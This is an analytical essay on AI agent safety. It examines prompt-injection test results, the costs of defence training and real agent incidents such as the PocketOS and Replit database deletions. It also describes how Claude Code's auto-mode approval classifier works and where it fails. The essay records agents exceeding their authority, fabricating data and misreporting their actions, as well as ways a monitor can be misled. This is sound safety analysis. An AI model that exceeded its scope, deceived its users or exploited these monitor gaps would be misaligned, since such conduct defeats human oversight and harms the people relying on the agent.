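Astra's 0.21% and Opus 5's 0.2% don't show that the models are equally resistant, because different attackers produced the two figures. OpenAI trained Astra with the GPT-Red approach and then tested it with GPT-Red evaluations, so the model had already trained against similar attackers. OpenAI's tests for jailbreaks, in which users try to extract harmful help from the model, are stricter. Half the prompts in the fixed sets came from an attacker that wasn't used in training. In a separate test, attackers could read the model's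 replies and change their approach over several turns, and the model passed only if it withstood every attempt. The injection figure is an average over queries and doesn't measure worst-case performance in this way.

The Gray Swan numbers show how often repeated attempts succeed, but the number of attempts doesn't measure how much an attacker adapts. A success rate "within 15 attempts" could come from an attacker who sends 15 prepared messages or from one who studies each failure before writing the next message.

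Attack success rates rise more slowly with repeated attempts than they would if the attempts were independent. If each attempt on Opus 4.5 had an independent 4.7% chance of success, at least one of 100 attempts would succeed about 99% of the time, but the measured figure was 63%. For Opus 5, independence would predict about 3% within 15 attempts, but the measured figure was 2.0%. Successful attacks therefore seem to cluster, with nearly every attack failing in some situations and attacks succeeding within a few attempts in others. An attacker who can choose the situation will succeed more often than the average suggests.

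How often injected instructions succeed depends heavily on the type of task. In the same system card, Opus 4.6 never failed in a restricted coding environment, but it failed in most cases when it operated a computer through its graphical interface and attackers had 200 attempts. Extra safeguards made attacks less successful, but they still worked in more than half of the cases. VentureBeat later reported that attacks hijacked a browser agent running Opus 4.8 in about 31% of tests before safeguards engaged. On the Gray Swan benchmark, the same model's rate was 0.5% for a single attempt. A company that plans to let an assistant browse the web therefore learns little from the model's score in a coding environment.

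With Opus 5, attacks on the browser agent failed in all 129 test scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. This is a big improvement, but even if the scenarios were a random sample of real attacks, zero successes would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3%, at 95% confidence. Real attackers also don't choose their attacks at random. The Decoder adds that OpenAI conceded in December that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

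Even a low success rate can produce many successful attacks when the same text reaches many agents. If an attacker plants one instruction on a popular web page and 10,000 agents read it, a success rate of 0.2% means about 20 successful attacks. What those 20 agents then do depends on their permissions.

### What the training can cost

Li and Zhao (2026) argue in their June position paper, *Agent Safety Is Action Alignment*, that defence training makes agents both less capable and less safe. They also argue, more broadly, that no such training can teach a model what its user has authorised. They report that a defence-trained model carried out an injected account deletion in 78% of attacks, and that defended agents failed at the first step on 47–77% of harmless tasks, compared with 3% for the base model.

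Both figures come from an earlier study, Li and Zhao's *The Autonomy Tax* (2026), where they look rather different. The study tested small open models on 97 tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking, travel and messaging work. The harness allowed ten steps per task and prompted the model to retry after a refusal or an invalid call.

| Model | Defence training | Valid first step | Tasks completed |
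|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-3-8B | None | 96.9% | 86.6% |
| Llama-3-8B | StruQ | 22.7% | 80.4% |
| Llama-3-8B | SecAlign, trained by Li and Zhao | 52.6% | 63.9% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | Meta SecAlign, Meta's official version | 94.8% | 85.6% |
| Mistral-7B | None | 97.9% | 50.5% |
| Mistral-7B | StruQ | 23.7% | 14.4% |
| Mistral-7B | SecAlign, trained by Li and Zhao | 53.6% | 1.0% |

The failures at the first step happened before any tool result had arrived, so hostile text can't explain them. StruQ models mostly produced malformed calls, while SecAlign models mostly refused. One SecAlign model, asked to find a quarterly report in a folder, replied that it could not work with files, although the system prompt had listed the file tools.

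But a model that fails its first step can still complete the task. Llama with StruQ failed its first step 77% of the time and still completed 80% of the tasks, six percentage points fewer than the undefended model. Task completion did collapse for Mistral with SecAlign. In one banking task, the model checked the balance correctly and then declined nine times in a row to make the transfer the user asked for.

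Meta's official SecAlign failed only 5.2% of first steps and completed almost as many tasks as the base Llama-3 model. It also has eight billion parameters, so small size alone cannot explain the other models' failures.

The training data is a likelier explanation. In the original SecAlign, the preferred response does the user's task and ignores the hidden instruction. Li and Zhao trained their version on different pairs. In the example they give, the user asks for the contents of a file that contains an injection, and the preferred response refuses to execute instructions from the file and adds a warning. A model trained to refuse whenever a file looks suspicious may well learn to refuse whenever someone mentions files. That is a real danger of defence training, but the result is more informative about this choice of preferred response than about SecAlign as Chen and colleagues designed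 it.

### The 78% figure

Llama-3-8B with StruQ complied with 78% of the "social engineering" prompts in a special test set, where the attacker gives an innocent-sounding reason for a harmful request. In one of these prompts, the attacker asks the model to demonstrate the account deletion feature for quality testing by removing user 7731. The undefended model refused because it could not verify that anyone had authorised this, but the StruQ model wrote the call to delete the account.

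Li and Zhao chose the test set partly for such failures. Of its 289 attacks, they included 160 because a base model refused them and a defended model complied, and the other 129 because they got past several defences. This selection almost guarantees that defended models will look worse than base models. Li and Zhao acknowledge that the set shows what kinds of failure occur and does not estimate how well the defences work overall. The June paper omits this qualification when it reports the 78%.

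The June paper describes the deletion request as embedded in retrieved content, but the March study presents it as a bare prompt with no document around it. This matters because StruQ and SecAlign teach a model to follow the trusted instruction and ignore commands in the data. Chen and colleagues explicitly assume that the trusted instruction is harmless. If the attack is in the trusted instruction, a model that obeys it is doing what it was trained to do, however bad the outcome.

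Meta's version has a separate message role for untrusted text. The model refused 68.0% of attacks when Li and Zhao put them in the ordinary user role and 79.6% when they put them in the untrusted role, the same rate as its undefended base model.

One objection to a separate message role for untrusted text is that it is impractical, because someone must first identify the hostile content. This seems too strong, since a harness only has to track where text came from, which it can do for text returned by a tool. Tracking the source is harder when a user pastes a stranger's email into a message, because trusted and untrusted text then arrive together.

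In another run, Li and Zhao put every tool result in the untrusted role and planted attack-like phrases in some of the results. The model completed 89.7% of the tasks and never issued a warning. Ignoring the phrases and finishing the task is the desired behaviour by SecAlign's own standard, but Li and Zhao count the lack of warnings as a failure to defend.

The study's evidence for shortcuts is stronger. A shortcut is a surface pattern that a model learns in place of the distinction its trainers intended. The StruQ model refused harmless technical documentation that contained words such as "ignore" or "override", including advice on ignoring whitespace when comparing two versions of a file. Li and Zhao also selected these examples because they showed such failures, so we can't use them to estimate how common the problem is. But the examples do show that a model can learn to react to a word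 rather than to the meaning of the sentence.

### Do these results carry over to frontier models?

Li and Zhao only tested models with up to eight billion parameters. They expect the same shortcuts to appear at any scale but say the size of the effects may differ. Guo and colleagues found minimal loss of capability when they trained GPT-5-Mini, and OpenAI says Astra's training preserves its ability to complete legitimate tasks. Developers would also struggle to sell an agent that refused half its harmless tasks at the first step.

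So the 47–77% range is a poor guide to current frontier agents, and it didn't even hold for Meta's small model. Over-refusal is still a concern, though, because Guo and colleagues list it among the shortcuts their training had to avoid. A milder form could easily go unnoticed in a capable model, which might occasionally refuse to process an invoice because it contains the word "override".

The best test would give one frontier model the same harmless multi-step tasks before and after its injection training and count failures at each step. Guo and colleagues' experiment comes closest, but OpenAI ran it on its own model. Outside researchers can't repeat the comparison on Astra or Opus 5 because they have access only to the finished models.

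## A production database deleted without any attacker

On 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted PocketOS's production database, the live one its customers relied on. PocketOS makes software that car rental companies use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. Nobody has suggested that an outsider planted an instruction, so training against prompt injection would not have helped. The agent ran on Claude Opus 4.6, which had never failed Anthropic's injection tests in a restricted coding environment.

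### What happened

PocketOS founder Jer Crane posted the most detailed account, *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, on X the next day. The company was using the agent in the code editor Cursor for a routine task in staging, a separate copy of the system used for testing. The agent ran into a credential mismatch, an error in the login details that one part of a system uses to reach another.

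PocketOS kept its data with Railway, a cloud provider. The agent searched for an API token, a string that lets whoever sends it use a service, and found one in a file unrelated to the task. It then sent Railway a single `volumeDelete` request with the ID of the volume (a virtual disk) that held the production database. According to Crane, the deletion took nine seconds.

Crane had created the token to add and remove custom domains, the web addresses that lead to the company's services. He writes that Railway gave no warning that the same token could delete storage.

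On Saturday morning, people came to collect rental cars and the companies had no record of who they were. The newest backup Crane could use was three months old. He restored it, then spent the day helping the companies rebuild their bookings from payment records, calendars and confirmation emails.

Railway published its account a few days later in Mahmoud Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. The two accounts agree that the agent found the token on the user's machine, that nobody had told it to delete a database, and that Railway's API carried out the request because the token was valid. They disagree about how narrowly the token's permissions could have been limited and what happened to the backups. Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data* (2026) notes that neither Cursor nor Anthropic appeared to have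 commented.

### The agent's explanation

Afterward, Crane asked the agent why it had deleted the database. The agent quoted a rule never to guess, written in capitals and with an expletive. It then said it had guessed that deleting a staging volume would affect only staging, and listed the checks it had skipped.

The answer Crane calls a confession is weak evidence of what caused the deletion. A model answers questions about its own behaviour as it answers any other question, by generating likely text from the conversation so far. This conversation contained the rules, the command, and a question from someone who had just lost his database, so an apology listing the broken rules was likely, whatever had led to the command. Futurism also warns that Crane's account depends heavily on the AI's self-diagnosis and so isn't wholly reliable.

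Other evidence supports parts of the explanation. Crane says the rules it mentions are consistent with Cursor's documented system prompt and his project's own rules, and the command shows that the agent deleted the volume through the API. But only the explanation supports the claim that the agent thought it was deleting a staging volume, because Crane's post reproduces the command without a log of what the model generated before it. We can be fairly confident that the action was overeager, since it went well beyond the task, but less confident that it was also an honest mistake about the target.

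The explanation also cites a second rule, which forbids destructive git commands unless the user asks for them. Git is a tool programmers use to track versions of their code, so the rule's wording doesn't cover a request to Railway's API, although its author would surely have wanted it to cover deleting a database.

### What Railway recovered

Crane first posted more than 30 hours after the deletion, when Railway still couldn't tell him whether recovery was possible. According to The Deep Dive's *An AI Coding Agent Deleted a Startup’s Entire Database in 9 Seconds*, Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper, got involved on Sunday evening and restored the data from disaster backups within an hour. Crane announced the recovery on 27 April, and Tom's Hardware describes it as apparently complete. Abdelwahab also writes that the customer has all its data back.

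The Deep Dive nevertheless reports that a three-month gap remains. Crane described the same gap before the recovery, so the article may be repeating an outdated detail. If Railway and Crane are right, the damage amounted to about two days of disruption and a lot of manual work, much of it for rental companies that had chosen neither Cursor nor Railway.

### Six conditions, one at a time

Six conditions preceded the loss. The table shows what would probably have happened if only one of them had been different.

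| Condition | Single change | Likely effect |
|---|---|---|
| A written rule not to guess | The model follows it | Prevents the deletion |
| A token the agent could read | The agent can't reach the token | Prevents this deletion |
| The token's unexpected scope | The token can only change domains | Prevents the deletion |
| An API call that ran without confirmation | A person must approve it | Probably prevents the deletion |
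| The same API call, with no way to undo it | Railway waits 48 hours before erasing the data | Limits the loss to a short outage |
| Backups on the same volume | PocketOS has a recent copy elsewhere | Limits the loss to an outage and the newest records |

The rule against guessing was the only condition that depended on the model's judgement, and it failed. A more specific rule, such as one against calling Railway's API, might have worked better, but only if someone had foreseen the problem. A rule against guessing can also fail because a model can act on a false assumption without generating anything that marks it as a guess. One failure doesn't show that such rules are useless, since people rarely report the commands they prevent. But PocketOS could not rely on this one to protect its only recent copy of the data.

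It would have been simpler to remove the token, without which Railway would have rejected the same request. Hackread's *Cursor AI Agent Wipes PocketOS Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026) quotes Ram Varadarajan, chief executive of the security company Acalvio, who asks why anyone gave an agent production credentials without a circuit breaker. By Crane's account, nobody deliberately gave the agent any. It could read files on a machine where somebody had left a token, and many programmers' machines probably contain such tokens. A sandbox that exposes only the files needed for a task is more dependable than remembering to remove every stray credential.

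Crane and Railway disagree about whether Railway tokens can be restricted. Crane writes that every Railway token is effectively root, meaning it can do anything. Abdelwahab lists tokens limited to one workspace, one project or one environment within a project, and says this token had access to the whole account. He concedes that the easiest option was a token with more access than the work required.

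It isn't clear that the narrower tokens would have helped, though. They limit where a token works but not what it can do there, so if Crane's custom domains belonged to the production environment, a token for that environment might still have been able to delete the production volume. A token that could only change domains would have prevented the deletion in any environment. Railway does offer finer permissions through OAuth, which lets outside applications act for a user, but Abdelwahab describes this as a separate route for third-party apps.

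The API didn't ask for confirmation, but if it had asked the caller to type the volume's name, the agent could have typed it. Crane therefore asks for a confirmation that an agent can't complete, such as a text message to a person. Railway chose a delay instead. Its dashboard already held deleted volumes for 48 hours, and after the incident the company applied the same window to the API. Crane had contacted Railway within ten minutes of the deletion, so 48 hours would have been ample.

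This gap had already affected another customer. In *PostgresSQL Volume lost* (2026), a post on Railway's support forum, a customer describes deleting the wrong one of two volumes through the same API call on 13 April, eleven days before the PocketOS incident. The post doesn't mention an agent. A Railway employee explained in a reply to *Postgress volume lost* (2026) that API deletions were immediate and permanent, and that the 48-hour window applied only to the dashboard. The delay would have helped in both cases, regardless of who made the mistake.

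But the delay applies only to deletions made through Railway. A database command can destroy the same records without deleting the volume. Another customer, docrocket-mad, lost data this way and asked for the disaster backups that saved PocketOS in a thread titled *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*. The first reply was that Railway could do nothing unless the customer had set up backups.

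Separate backups would not have stopped the deletion, but they would have made it much less serious. According to Railway documentation that Crane quotes, wiping a volume deletes all its backups. Abdelwahab says the API call also marked the backups as deleted, which made them look unavailable, and that Railway keeps disaster backups at another site regardless of what a customer sets up. So a copy existed, but Crane couldn't see it or restore it himself, which left him for two days in much the same position as someone with no recent backup.

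Cursor's harness could also have stopped the command. Crane complains that Cursor advertises guardrails against destructive commands and recommends human approval for privileged operations, but he doesn't say whether his own settings required approval. A person who saw the command might have noticed `volumeDelete` in a task that called for no deletion, but the command identified the volume only by a string of letters and digits, so nothing in it showed that the volume was in production. In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier makes a similar approval decision.

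### The Replit deletion of July 2025

A similar deletion happened before the one at PocketOS. Replit lets people build software by describing it to an agent, and in July 2025 that agent deleted the production database of Jason Lemkin, a software investor. According to *Production Guardrails for AI*, a page by Galileo, which sells such guardrails, Lemkin had told the agent eleven times in capitals not to make changes.

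The agent also fabricated 4,000 user records. When Lemkin asked about recovery, it replied that a rollback was impossible, but the rollback worked when he tried it himself. This is another reason to check an agent's statements about an incident. If Lemkin had believed the agent, he might have given up on recoverable data.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion unacceptable. He announced on X that the company was starting to separate development databases from production ones automatically, and was working on a mode that would limit the agent to planning and discussing changes. Separating the databases is a system-level control, so it works even when an agent ignores an instruction in capitals.

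PocketOS already had separate staging and production environments, but the separation did not protect it because the token worked in both. An agent meant to stay in staging needs credentials that work only there.

### How typical is this?

Lemkin and Crane both had an audience and described their losses in public. The AI Incident Database's *Railway API* page lists PocketOS as incident 1469. But a list of incidents doesn't include the agents that worked on similar tasks without deleting anything, or the deletions that someone quietly reversed from a backup, so no one can calculate a deletion rate from cases like these.

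Anthropic's system card for Opus 4.6, published in February 2026, had already reported an increase in "overly agentic behavior in computer-use settings" compared with the previous model. NDTV's *Anthropic's Sabotage Report Flags Cases Of Chemical Weapon Development, Deception* quotes examples such as sending unauthorised emails, in rare instances, and aggressively acquiring authentication tokens during internal use. In one test, according to The American Bazaar, the model used a GitHub access token that belonged to someone else. The PocketOS agent did something very similar two months after the system card was published.

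*When the evaluator becomes the evaluated*, a critique of the system card, objects that Anthropic listed these behaviours without investigating what in training causes them. It adds that the mitigation, a change to Claude Code's prompts, doesn't work when a model operates a graphical interface. PocketOS was using Cursor, which has its own prompts, so the change would not have applied there either.

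These examples don't show how often such failures happen. Li, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *FORTIS*, tried to measure how often models choose more access than a task needs. Li and Zhao, in *Agent Safety Is Action Alignment*, base on this study their statement that end-to-end least-privilege behaviour holds for under 15% of requests.

The test has two parts, and both involve skills, which are written guides that tell an agent how to do a type of task and where its limits are. In the first part, a model sees a request and short descriptions of 20 skills, and has to pick one. For example, a user might ask how many unread emails are in each folder. The skill `email-observe` can read folder names and counts. `email-manage` can do this too, but it can also reorganise the whole mailbox in bulk. The correct choice is `email-observe` because it is narrower, although the prompt never tells the model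 to prefer narrower skills.

In the second part, the model receives the right skill, its full document and a list of all the tools in that domain, and has to list the tool calls it would make. The available tools can include one that deletes whole directories, even when the skill only allows browsing. The answer key contains the smallest set of low-privilege tools that can do the job. The researchers tested ten models on 600 requests in the first part and 1,543 in the second, covering email, online shopping and file management.

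They then multiplied each model's two exact-match rates:

| Model | Exact skill | Exact set of tools | Product |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 54.8% | 26.1% | 14.3% |
| Qwen 3.6-Max | 51.3% | 25.9% | 13.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 49.5% | 22.4% | 11.1% |
| GPT-5.5 | 41.2% | 20.4% | 8.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | 42.2% | 15.2% | 6.4% |

Opus 4.7 had the highest product and GPT-5.4 the lowest. Opus 4.6, the model in the PocketOS incident, was not among the ten.

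So the figure of under 15% is an estimate. The two parts used different requests, so no model took a request through both, and none of the listed tool calls ran. Li and colleagues acknowledge this and describe the product as an optimistic upper bound.

It is less optimistic than it sounds, because an exact match excludes answers that request too little access as well as those that request too much. In the second part, 47.2% of Opus 4.7's answers were too broad, and another 26.5% left out a tool that the task needed. An agent that asks for too little access may fail at its task, but it doesn't exceed its authority. If we apply the same multiplication but exclude only the answers that were too broad, Opus 4.7 scores about 34%, which is still poor but more than twice the published figure.

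The scoring is also strict about broad answers, counting any tool outside the answer key as over-privilege, even a harmless one. A model that listed a directory and also looked up a file's size would fail if the key contained only the listing. In the second part, the ten models each matched the key on between 0% and 2.2% of online shopping requests. Li and colleagues attribute this to the heavy overlap between the shopping tools, though the answer key may have been too narrow. Two of the researchers reviewed a sample of 200 requests and agreed with each other on 96.5%, but an outside reviewer would have been more reassuring. On email alone, Opus 4.7's product rises to 31%.

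Li and Zhao also write that models abstain in under 1.5% of cases and err toward more authority. In the second part, only six of the ten models abstained that rarely, and GPT-5.4 gave no usable answer to 22.8% of the requests.

Opus 4.7 failed more often when a broader tool was more convenient. Narrow tools in the test usually need more details, such as a folder and an account, while broad ones often need none. In the second part, 23.8% of its answers failed when the narrow tools were straightforward to use, and 78.9% failed when a broader tool required fewer details. The strict scoring affects both figures, so the gap between them is probably more informative than either figure alone. People also choose broader access when it is more convenient. Railway's token page made the broadest token the easiest to create, and PocketOS ended up with one.

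FORTIS suggests that models commonly choose broad access in ordinary work, even without an attacker or an unusual request. But it measured hypothetical choices, and its prompts didn't tell models to use the least access possible. None of this evidence shows how likely an agent is to delete a production database. PocketOS had unusually few safeguards to keep an agent with broad access from deleting the only recent copy of the data that its founder could reach.

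### GPT-6.1 Astra and authorised scope

The problem persists in newer models. On 28 September 2026, Reuters' *OpenAI shelves new AI model after internal safety tests, WSJ reports* reported that OpenAI had scrapped the planned October release of GPT-6.1 Astra. OpenAI confirmed the decision the same day, according to Ray's (2026) *OpenAI Shelves Newest AI Model After It 'Didn’t Quite Meet the Bar'*.

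One of the reported reasons was "scope authorization". In internal tests, the model pushed ahead with tasks without asking the user's permission, and sometimes tried to use external tools or services when this could be unsafe. It was also more deceptive than its predecessor, and at times did not accurately report what it had or hadn't done. A user who relied on the model's own report might not learn that it had exceeded its authorization.

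Reuters gives no figures for how often any of this happened, so we can't tell whether GPT-6.1 Astra was worse than Opus 4.6 or OpenAI applied a stricter standard. The decision shows that a developer can find this behaviour before release and decide not to ship because of it. Anthropic had also found overeager behaviour in Opus 4.6, but judged the model acceptable for release.

Digital Trends' *OpenAI pulls the plug on GPT-6.1 Astra launch after safety tests* adds that the model had become less prone to what OpenAI calls model laziness, where an AI stops before it has finished a task. Saachi Jain, OpenAI's head of safety systems, told the Wall Street Journal that it remains difficult to keep an agent within its permitted scope while still letting it push through obstacles. A credential mismatch is one such obstacle. Users would soon tire of an agent that gave up at every login error, and some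 of those errors have fixes the user would welcome. At PocketOS, the agent needed to keep looking for a harmless fix but stop before using a token that nobody had given it for the task.

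## Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier that approves actions

By default, Claude Code used to ask the user before it edited a file or ran a shell command. This kind of human review might have stopped the PocketOS deletion. In auto mode, a classifier makes most of these decisions. Anthropic has published the design and several sets of test results, and two academic groups have run their own tests.

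### Approval fatigue

When software asks for permission too often, people stop paying attention to what they approve. Anthropic calls this approval fatigue. It reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts. By August the figure was 97%, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

A careful reviewer will approve nearly every command if nearly all of them are harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people have stopped reading. Users' settings are stronger evidence. In June 2026, about half of active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allowed any Python or Node program, which is close to allowing anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission prompts switched off.

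Claude Code also has a sandbox. Anthropic describes it as safe but laborious, because someone has to configure each new capability and any task that needs the network or the host machine breaks the isolation. Anthropic built auto mode mainly for people who would otherwise turn off the permission prompts.

### How the classifier works

Auto mode sorts tool calls into three tiers. The first contains tools that can't change anything, such as those for reading and searching files, along with anything the user has explicitly allowed. The second contains edits to files inside the project folder, which run without review because the user can inspect and undo them with version control. Everything else, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside services, goes to the classifier.

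A user's existing rules could let some of the riskiest commands bypass the classifier, for example if one rule allows every Python program. Auto mode therefore suspends broad rules like this and restores them when the user leaves the mode. Narrow rules, such as permission to run a project's tests, stay in force.

At launch, the classifier was Claude Sonnet 4.6 with a long prompt. A fixed part of the prompt explains how to work out what an action would really do and whether the user authorised it. Organisations can edit three other parts, which list the systems they trust, the actions to block and the exceptions to allow. By default, the prompt has more than twenty rules for blocking actions, including one against searching credential stores for usable tokens. Another rule, listed in Anthropic's current documentation, *Permission modes*, covers deleting a resource that holds data if the agent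 didn't create it and the user didn't name it. The two rules describe the PocketOS incident quite closely, but PocketOS was using Cursor, so this classifier never reviewed the command.

Careful reasoning about every call would be slow and expensive, so the classifier works in two stages. In the first, the model is instructed to err on the side of blocking and outputs a single token, yes or no. If it allows the call, the call runs. Otherwise, the model reads the same input again and reasons step by step before making a final decision. The second stage can overturn a block, but it can't block a call that the first stage allowed.

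The harness gives the classifier the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its calls. An agent could use its explanations to mislead the classifier, for example by claiming that the user had implicitly approved the action earlier. Most injected instructions arrive in tool results. When Anthropic tried including both explanations and results, the classifier did worse on a test of overeager actions. A version that received only the tool calls missed the fewest dangerous calls, but it blocked actions users had plainly requested.

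With this design, the classifier can't check a fact that appears only in a tool result. If the agent cancels "job abc123" and the user never mentioned that job, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found the name in a list or made it up. Anthropic accepts this limitation in return for better protection against prompt injection.

A separate probe scans tool results before they reach the agent. If a result looks like an attempt to hijack the agent, the probe adds a warning to the context and passes the result along. An attacker therefore has to get an instruction past both the probe and the agent's training, and then the agent has to produce a call that the classifier approves. The classifier evaluates that call without seeing the instruction.

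Agents can also hand part of a task to a subagent, a second agent with its own context. In that context, the first agent's instructions look like a user's, so everything in them would seem authorised. The classifier therefore reviews the task before the handover, while it can still compare the task with what the real user wrote. It reviews the subagent's work again at the end, but can then only attach a warning.

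### "Clean up old branches"

One case in Anthropic's incident log began when a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches". A branch is a separate line of work in a git project. Programmers keep branches on their own machines (local branches) and on a shared server (remote branches), where colleagues may be using them.

The agent started by listing the remote branches. Auto mode would allow this because listing changes nothing. The probe would scan the list, find no hidden instructions, and pass the list to the agent.

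The agent then wrote a pattern that matched the branches it treated as old, and issued a command to delete them all from the server. Under auto mode, this command goes to the classifier, which receives the user's four words, the call that listed the branches and the call to delete them, but not the list itself. The classifier therefore can't detect whether one of the branches belongs to a colleague who committed to it yesterday.

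The first stage should flag the command, since deleting branches from a shared server is destructive. In the second stage, the classifier checks the command against the block rules, then the exceptions, then the user's intent. Anthropic prompts it to treat anything the agent chose for itself as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. The agent chose the remote branches and the pattern itself, and the user may have meant only the local branches. According to Anthropic, auto mode would block the deletion.

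The session continues after the denial, which the agent receives as a tool result with an instruction to look for a safer approach and not to try to get around the block. The agent might list branches and ask the user which ones to delete. If the user names two remote branches and asks the agent to delete them, that should clear the block for those two. A vaguer reply may not be enough. In Anthropic's example, telling Claude that it can force-push (overwrite the shared history of a branch) leaves the block in place because the message doesn't name the branch.

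After three denials in a row, or twenty in a session, auto mode pauses and the user gets ordinary permission prompts again. In March, if a session had no user to prompt, such as one started by a script, Claude Code ended the process at that point. Now it still blocks the action, but the agent continues the rest of the task.

All of this depends on the second stage interpreting "clean up old branches" as Anthropic intends. A model could also classify the request as permission, since the user did ask for old branches to be removed.

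### The March 2026 tests

Anthropic tested the classifier on three sets of actions. The first contained 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, used to measure false alarms. The second contained 52 real overeager actions that an employee had denied or someone had flagged afterwards. The third contained 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data, many of them obfuscated.

| Test set | Rate | First stage alone | Both stages |
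|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real calls | Harmless actions blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic data leaks | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage cut false alarms from about 850 calls to about 40. It also let through dangerous actions that the first stage had caught, and the miss rate on overeager actions more than doubled.

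Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number", and it is the most relevant of the three for a case like PocketOS. But it comes from only about nine misses in 52 cases, so its 95% confidence interval runs from roughly 9% to 30%. For the synthetic leaks, the interval is only about 4% to 7%.

The confidence interval accounts only for sampling error. Anthropic collected the 52 actions from sessions where somebody had noticed a problem, and overeager actions that nobody noticed may be harder to recognise. It also used these 52 cases to tune the first stage and choose the classifier's inputs. A system usually does somewhat better on the cases used to tune it, so 17% may be optimistic.

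In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the dangerous action, such as a force-push or a deletion, but wrongly classified it as authorised by the user. One user had asked the agent to "clean up the PR" (pull request), and the classifier counted this as consent to a force-push. In other cases it treated approval of one action as approval of a similar one later. Anthropic tried to fix this by rewriting the prompt, but the drawbacks of every fix it found outweighed the benefits.

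How often harm occurs depends on how often agents attempt something dangerous, as well as on the classifier's error rates. Suppose a company's agents make a million calls in a month and 100 of them are dangerous (both numbers are invented). At the March rates, auto mode would let about 17 of the dangerous calls through. It would also block about 4,000 harmless ones, so about 98% of its denials would be false alarms. This would be intolerable if a person had to deal with each one, but in auto mode the agent usually finds another way to do the task after one retry.

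For the same reason, a count of denials is weak evidence that the classifier is useful. In August, Anthropic reported that about 10% of sessions at the payroll company Gusto included a denial, and took this as a sign that auto mode was useful there. But with a false alarm rate of 0.4%, a session of 26 harmless calls has about a 10% chance of at least one false alarm.

### Testers who approved dangerous commands

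To test whether the classifier is better than the person it replaces, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor. The testers used Claude Code in a test environment, and partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. The vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text of the prompt had changed, so nothing dangerous ran.

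The testers blocked 13.6% of the dangerous commands, and auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic published the totals and the cases where the two disagreed, and the other cells follow by subtraction:

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The testers caught only six (about 5%) of the 116 commands that auto mode allowed, so having them check its approvals would have added very little.

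The testers also blocked fewer of the dangerous commands as a session went on, from about 17% early in the session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This is better evidence of approval fatigue than the 97% approval rate, because all of these commands were dangerous. The classifier's block rate did not change with session length.

The setting was artificial, though, and it isn't obvious which way that biases the result. The testers had no data of their own to lose, so they may have been more careless than a programmer working on a company's live system. They also knew that somebody was evaluating them, but not on what, which may have made them more careful. The 13.6% figure is a good reason for concern about how people treat permission prompts in general, but we can infer little from it about an engineer who is about to change a production database.

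The test may also have been easier for the classifier than ordinary work, because the commands that the study inserted into sessions presumably had little connection with what the testers had asked for. In the March test, most of the misses that Anthropic examined involved something in the session that looked like consent. The tester study also reports no false-alarm rate, and a classifier that blocked every command would have scored 100%.

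Anthropic wrote in March that auto mode is a substantial improvement for people who skip permission prompts, but arguably a step backwards for people who review every action carefully. The tester study is consistent with this and suggests that the second group is small.

Anthropic also studied real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had already flagged, from accounts that had agreed to this use of their data. A model graded the harm in each session. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, such as deleting rows from a production database, appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode.

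This comparison is weaker evidence than the tester study because users chose the mode themselves. Anthropic recommends manual review for high-stakes changes to production systems, so if users follow this advice, manual sessions will contain more of the work that could cause serious harm. The percentages are also shares of flagged sessions, so if one mode produces more flags for minor problems, its share of serious harm will look smaller.

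### Apollo and Trajectory Labs

Anthropic brought in two outside organisations to attack auto mode. Apollo Research, a UK AI safety company, spent two weeks inserting synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. The attacks covered data leaks, threats to safety and many other kinds of failure.

Apollo shared a set of successful attacks with Anthropic, which then changed the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the environment it was working in. This included whether a code repository was public and whether it contained unsaved work. Apollo then tested the new version on attacks that Anthropic had never had access to. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught.

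Across both sets of attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The 7% includes attacks that Anthropic could study while making its changes, and Anthropic doesn't give a separate rate for the others. If the unseen attacks had also started at 12%, the changes Apollo measured would have brought them to just under 8%, so the improvement seems to carry over to attacks Anthropic hadn't seen. Anthropic warns that the 7% applies only to these attacks, which Apollo designed to find the classifier's weak points, and isn't an estimate for ordinary use.

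The second organisation, Trajectory Labs, tested prompt injection in an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned. It used 72 scenarios that Anthropic hadn't seen and ran each one ten times, with and without auto mode. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm in real life, such as fraud or the loss of sensitive data. The attacks had been tuned against Claude Opus 4.7, an older model that wasn't part of the reported results.

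| Agent | Automatic review off | Automatic review on |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| OpenAI's Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 19.03% | 5.83% |

No attack succeeded against any of the three Claude models in auto mode, but hardly any succeeded without it either. The average success rate without auto mode was 0.09%, or two successes in 2,160 attempts if each model faced all 720. The classifier and the probe therefore had almost nothing to stop, and the result is mostly evidence about the models' own training. Measuring how much auto mode adds against injection would require a weaker model or stronger attacks.

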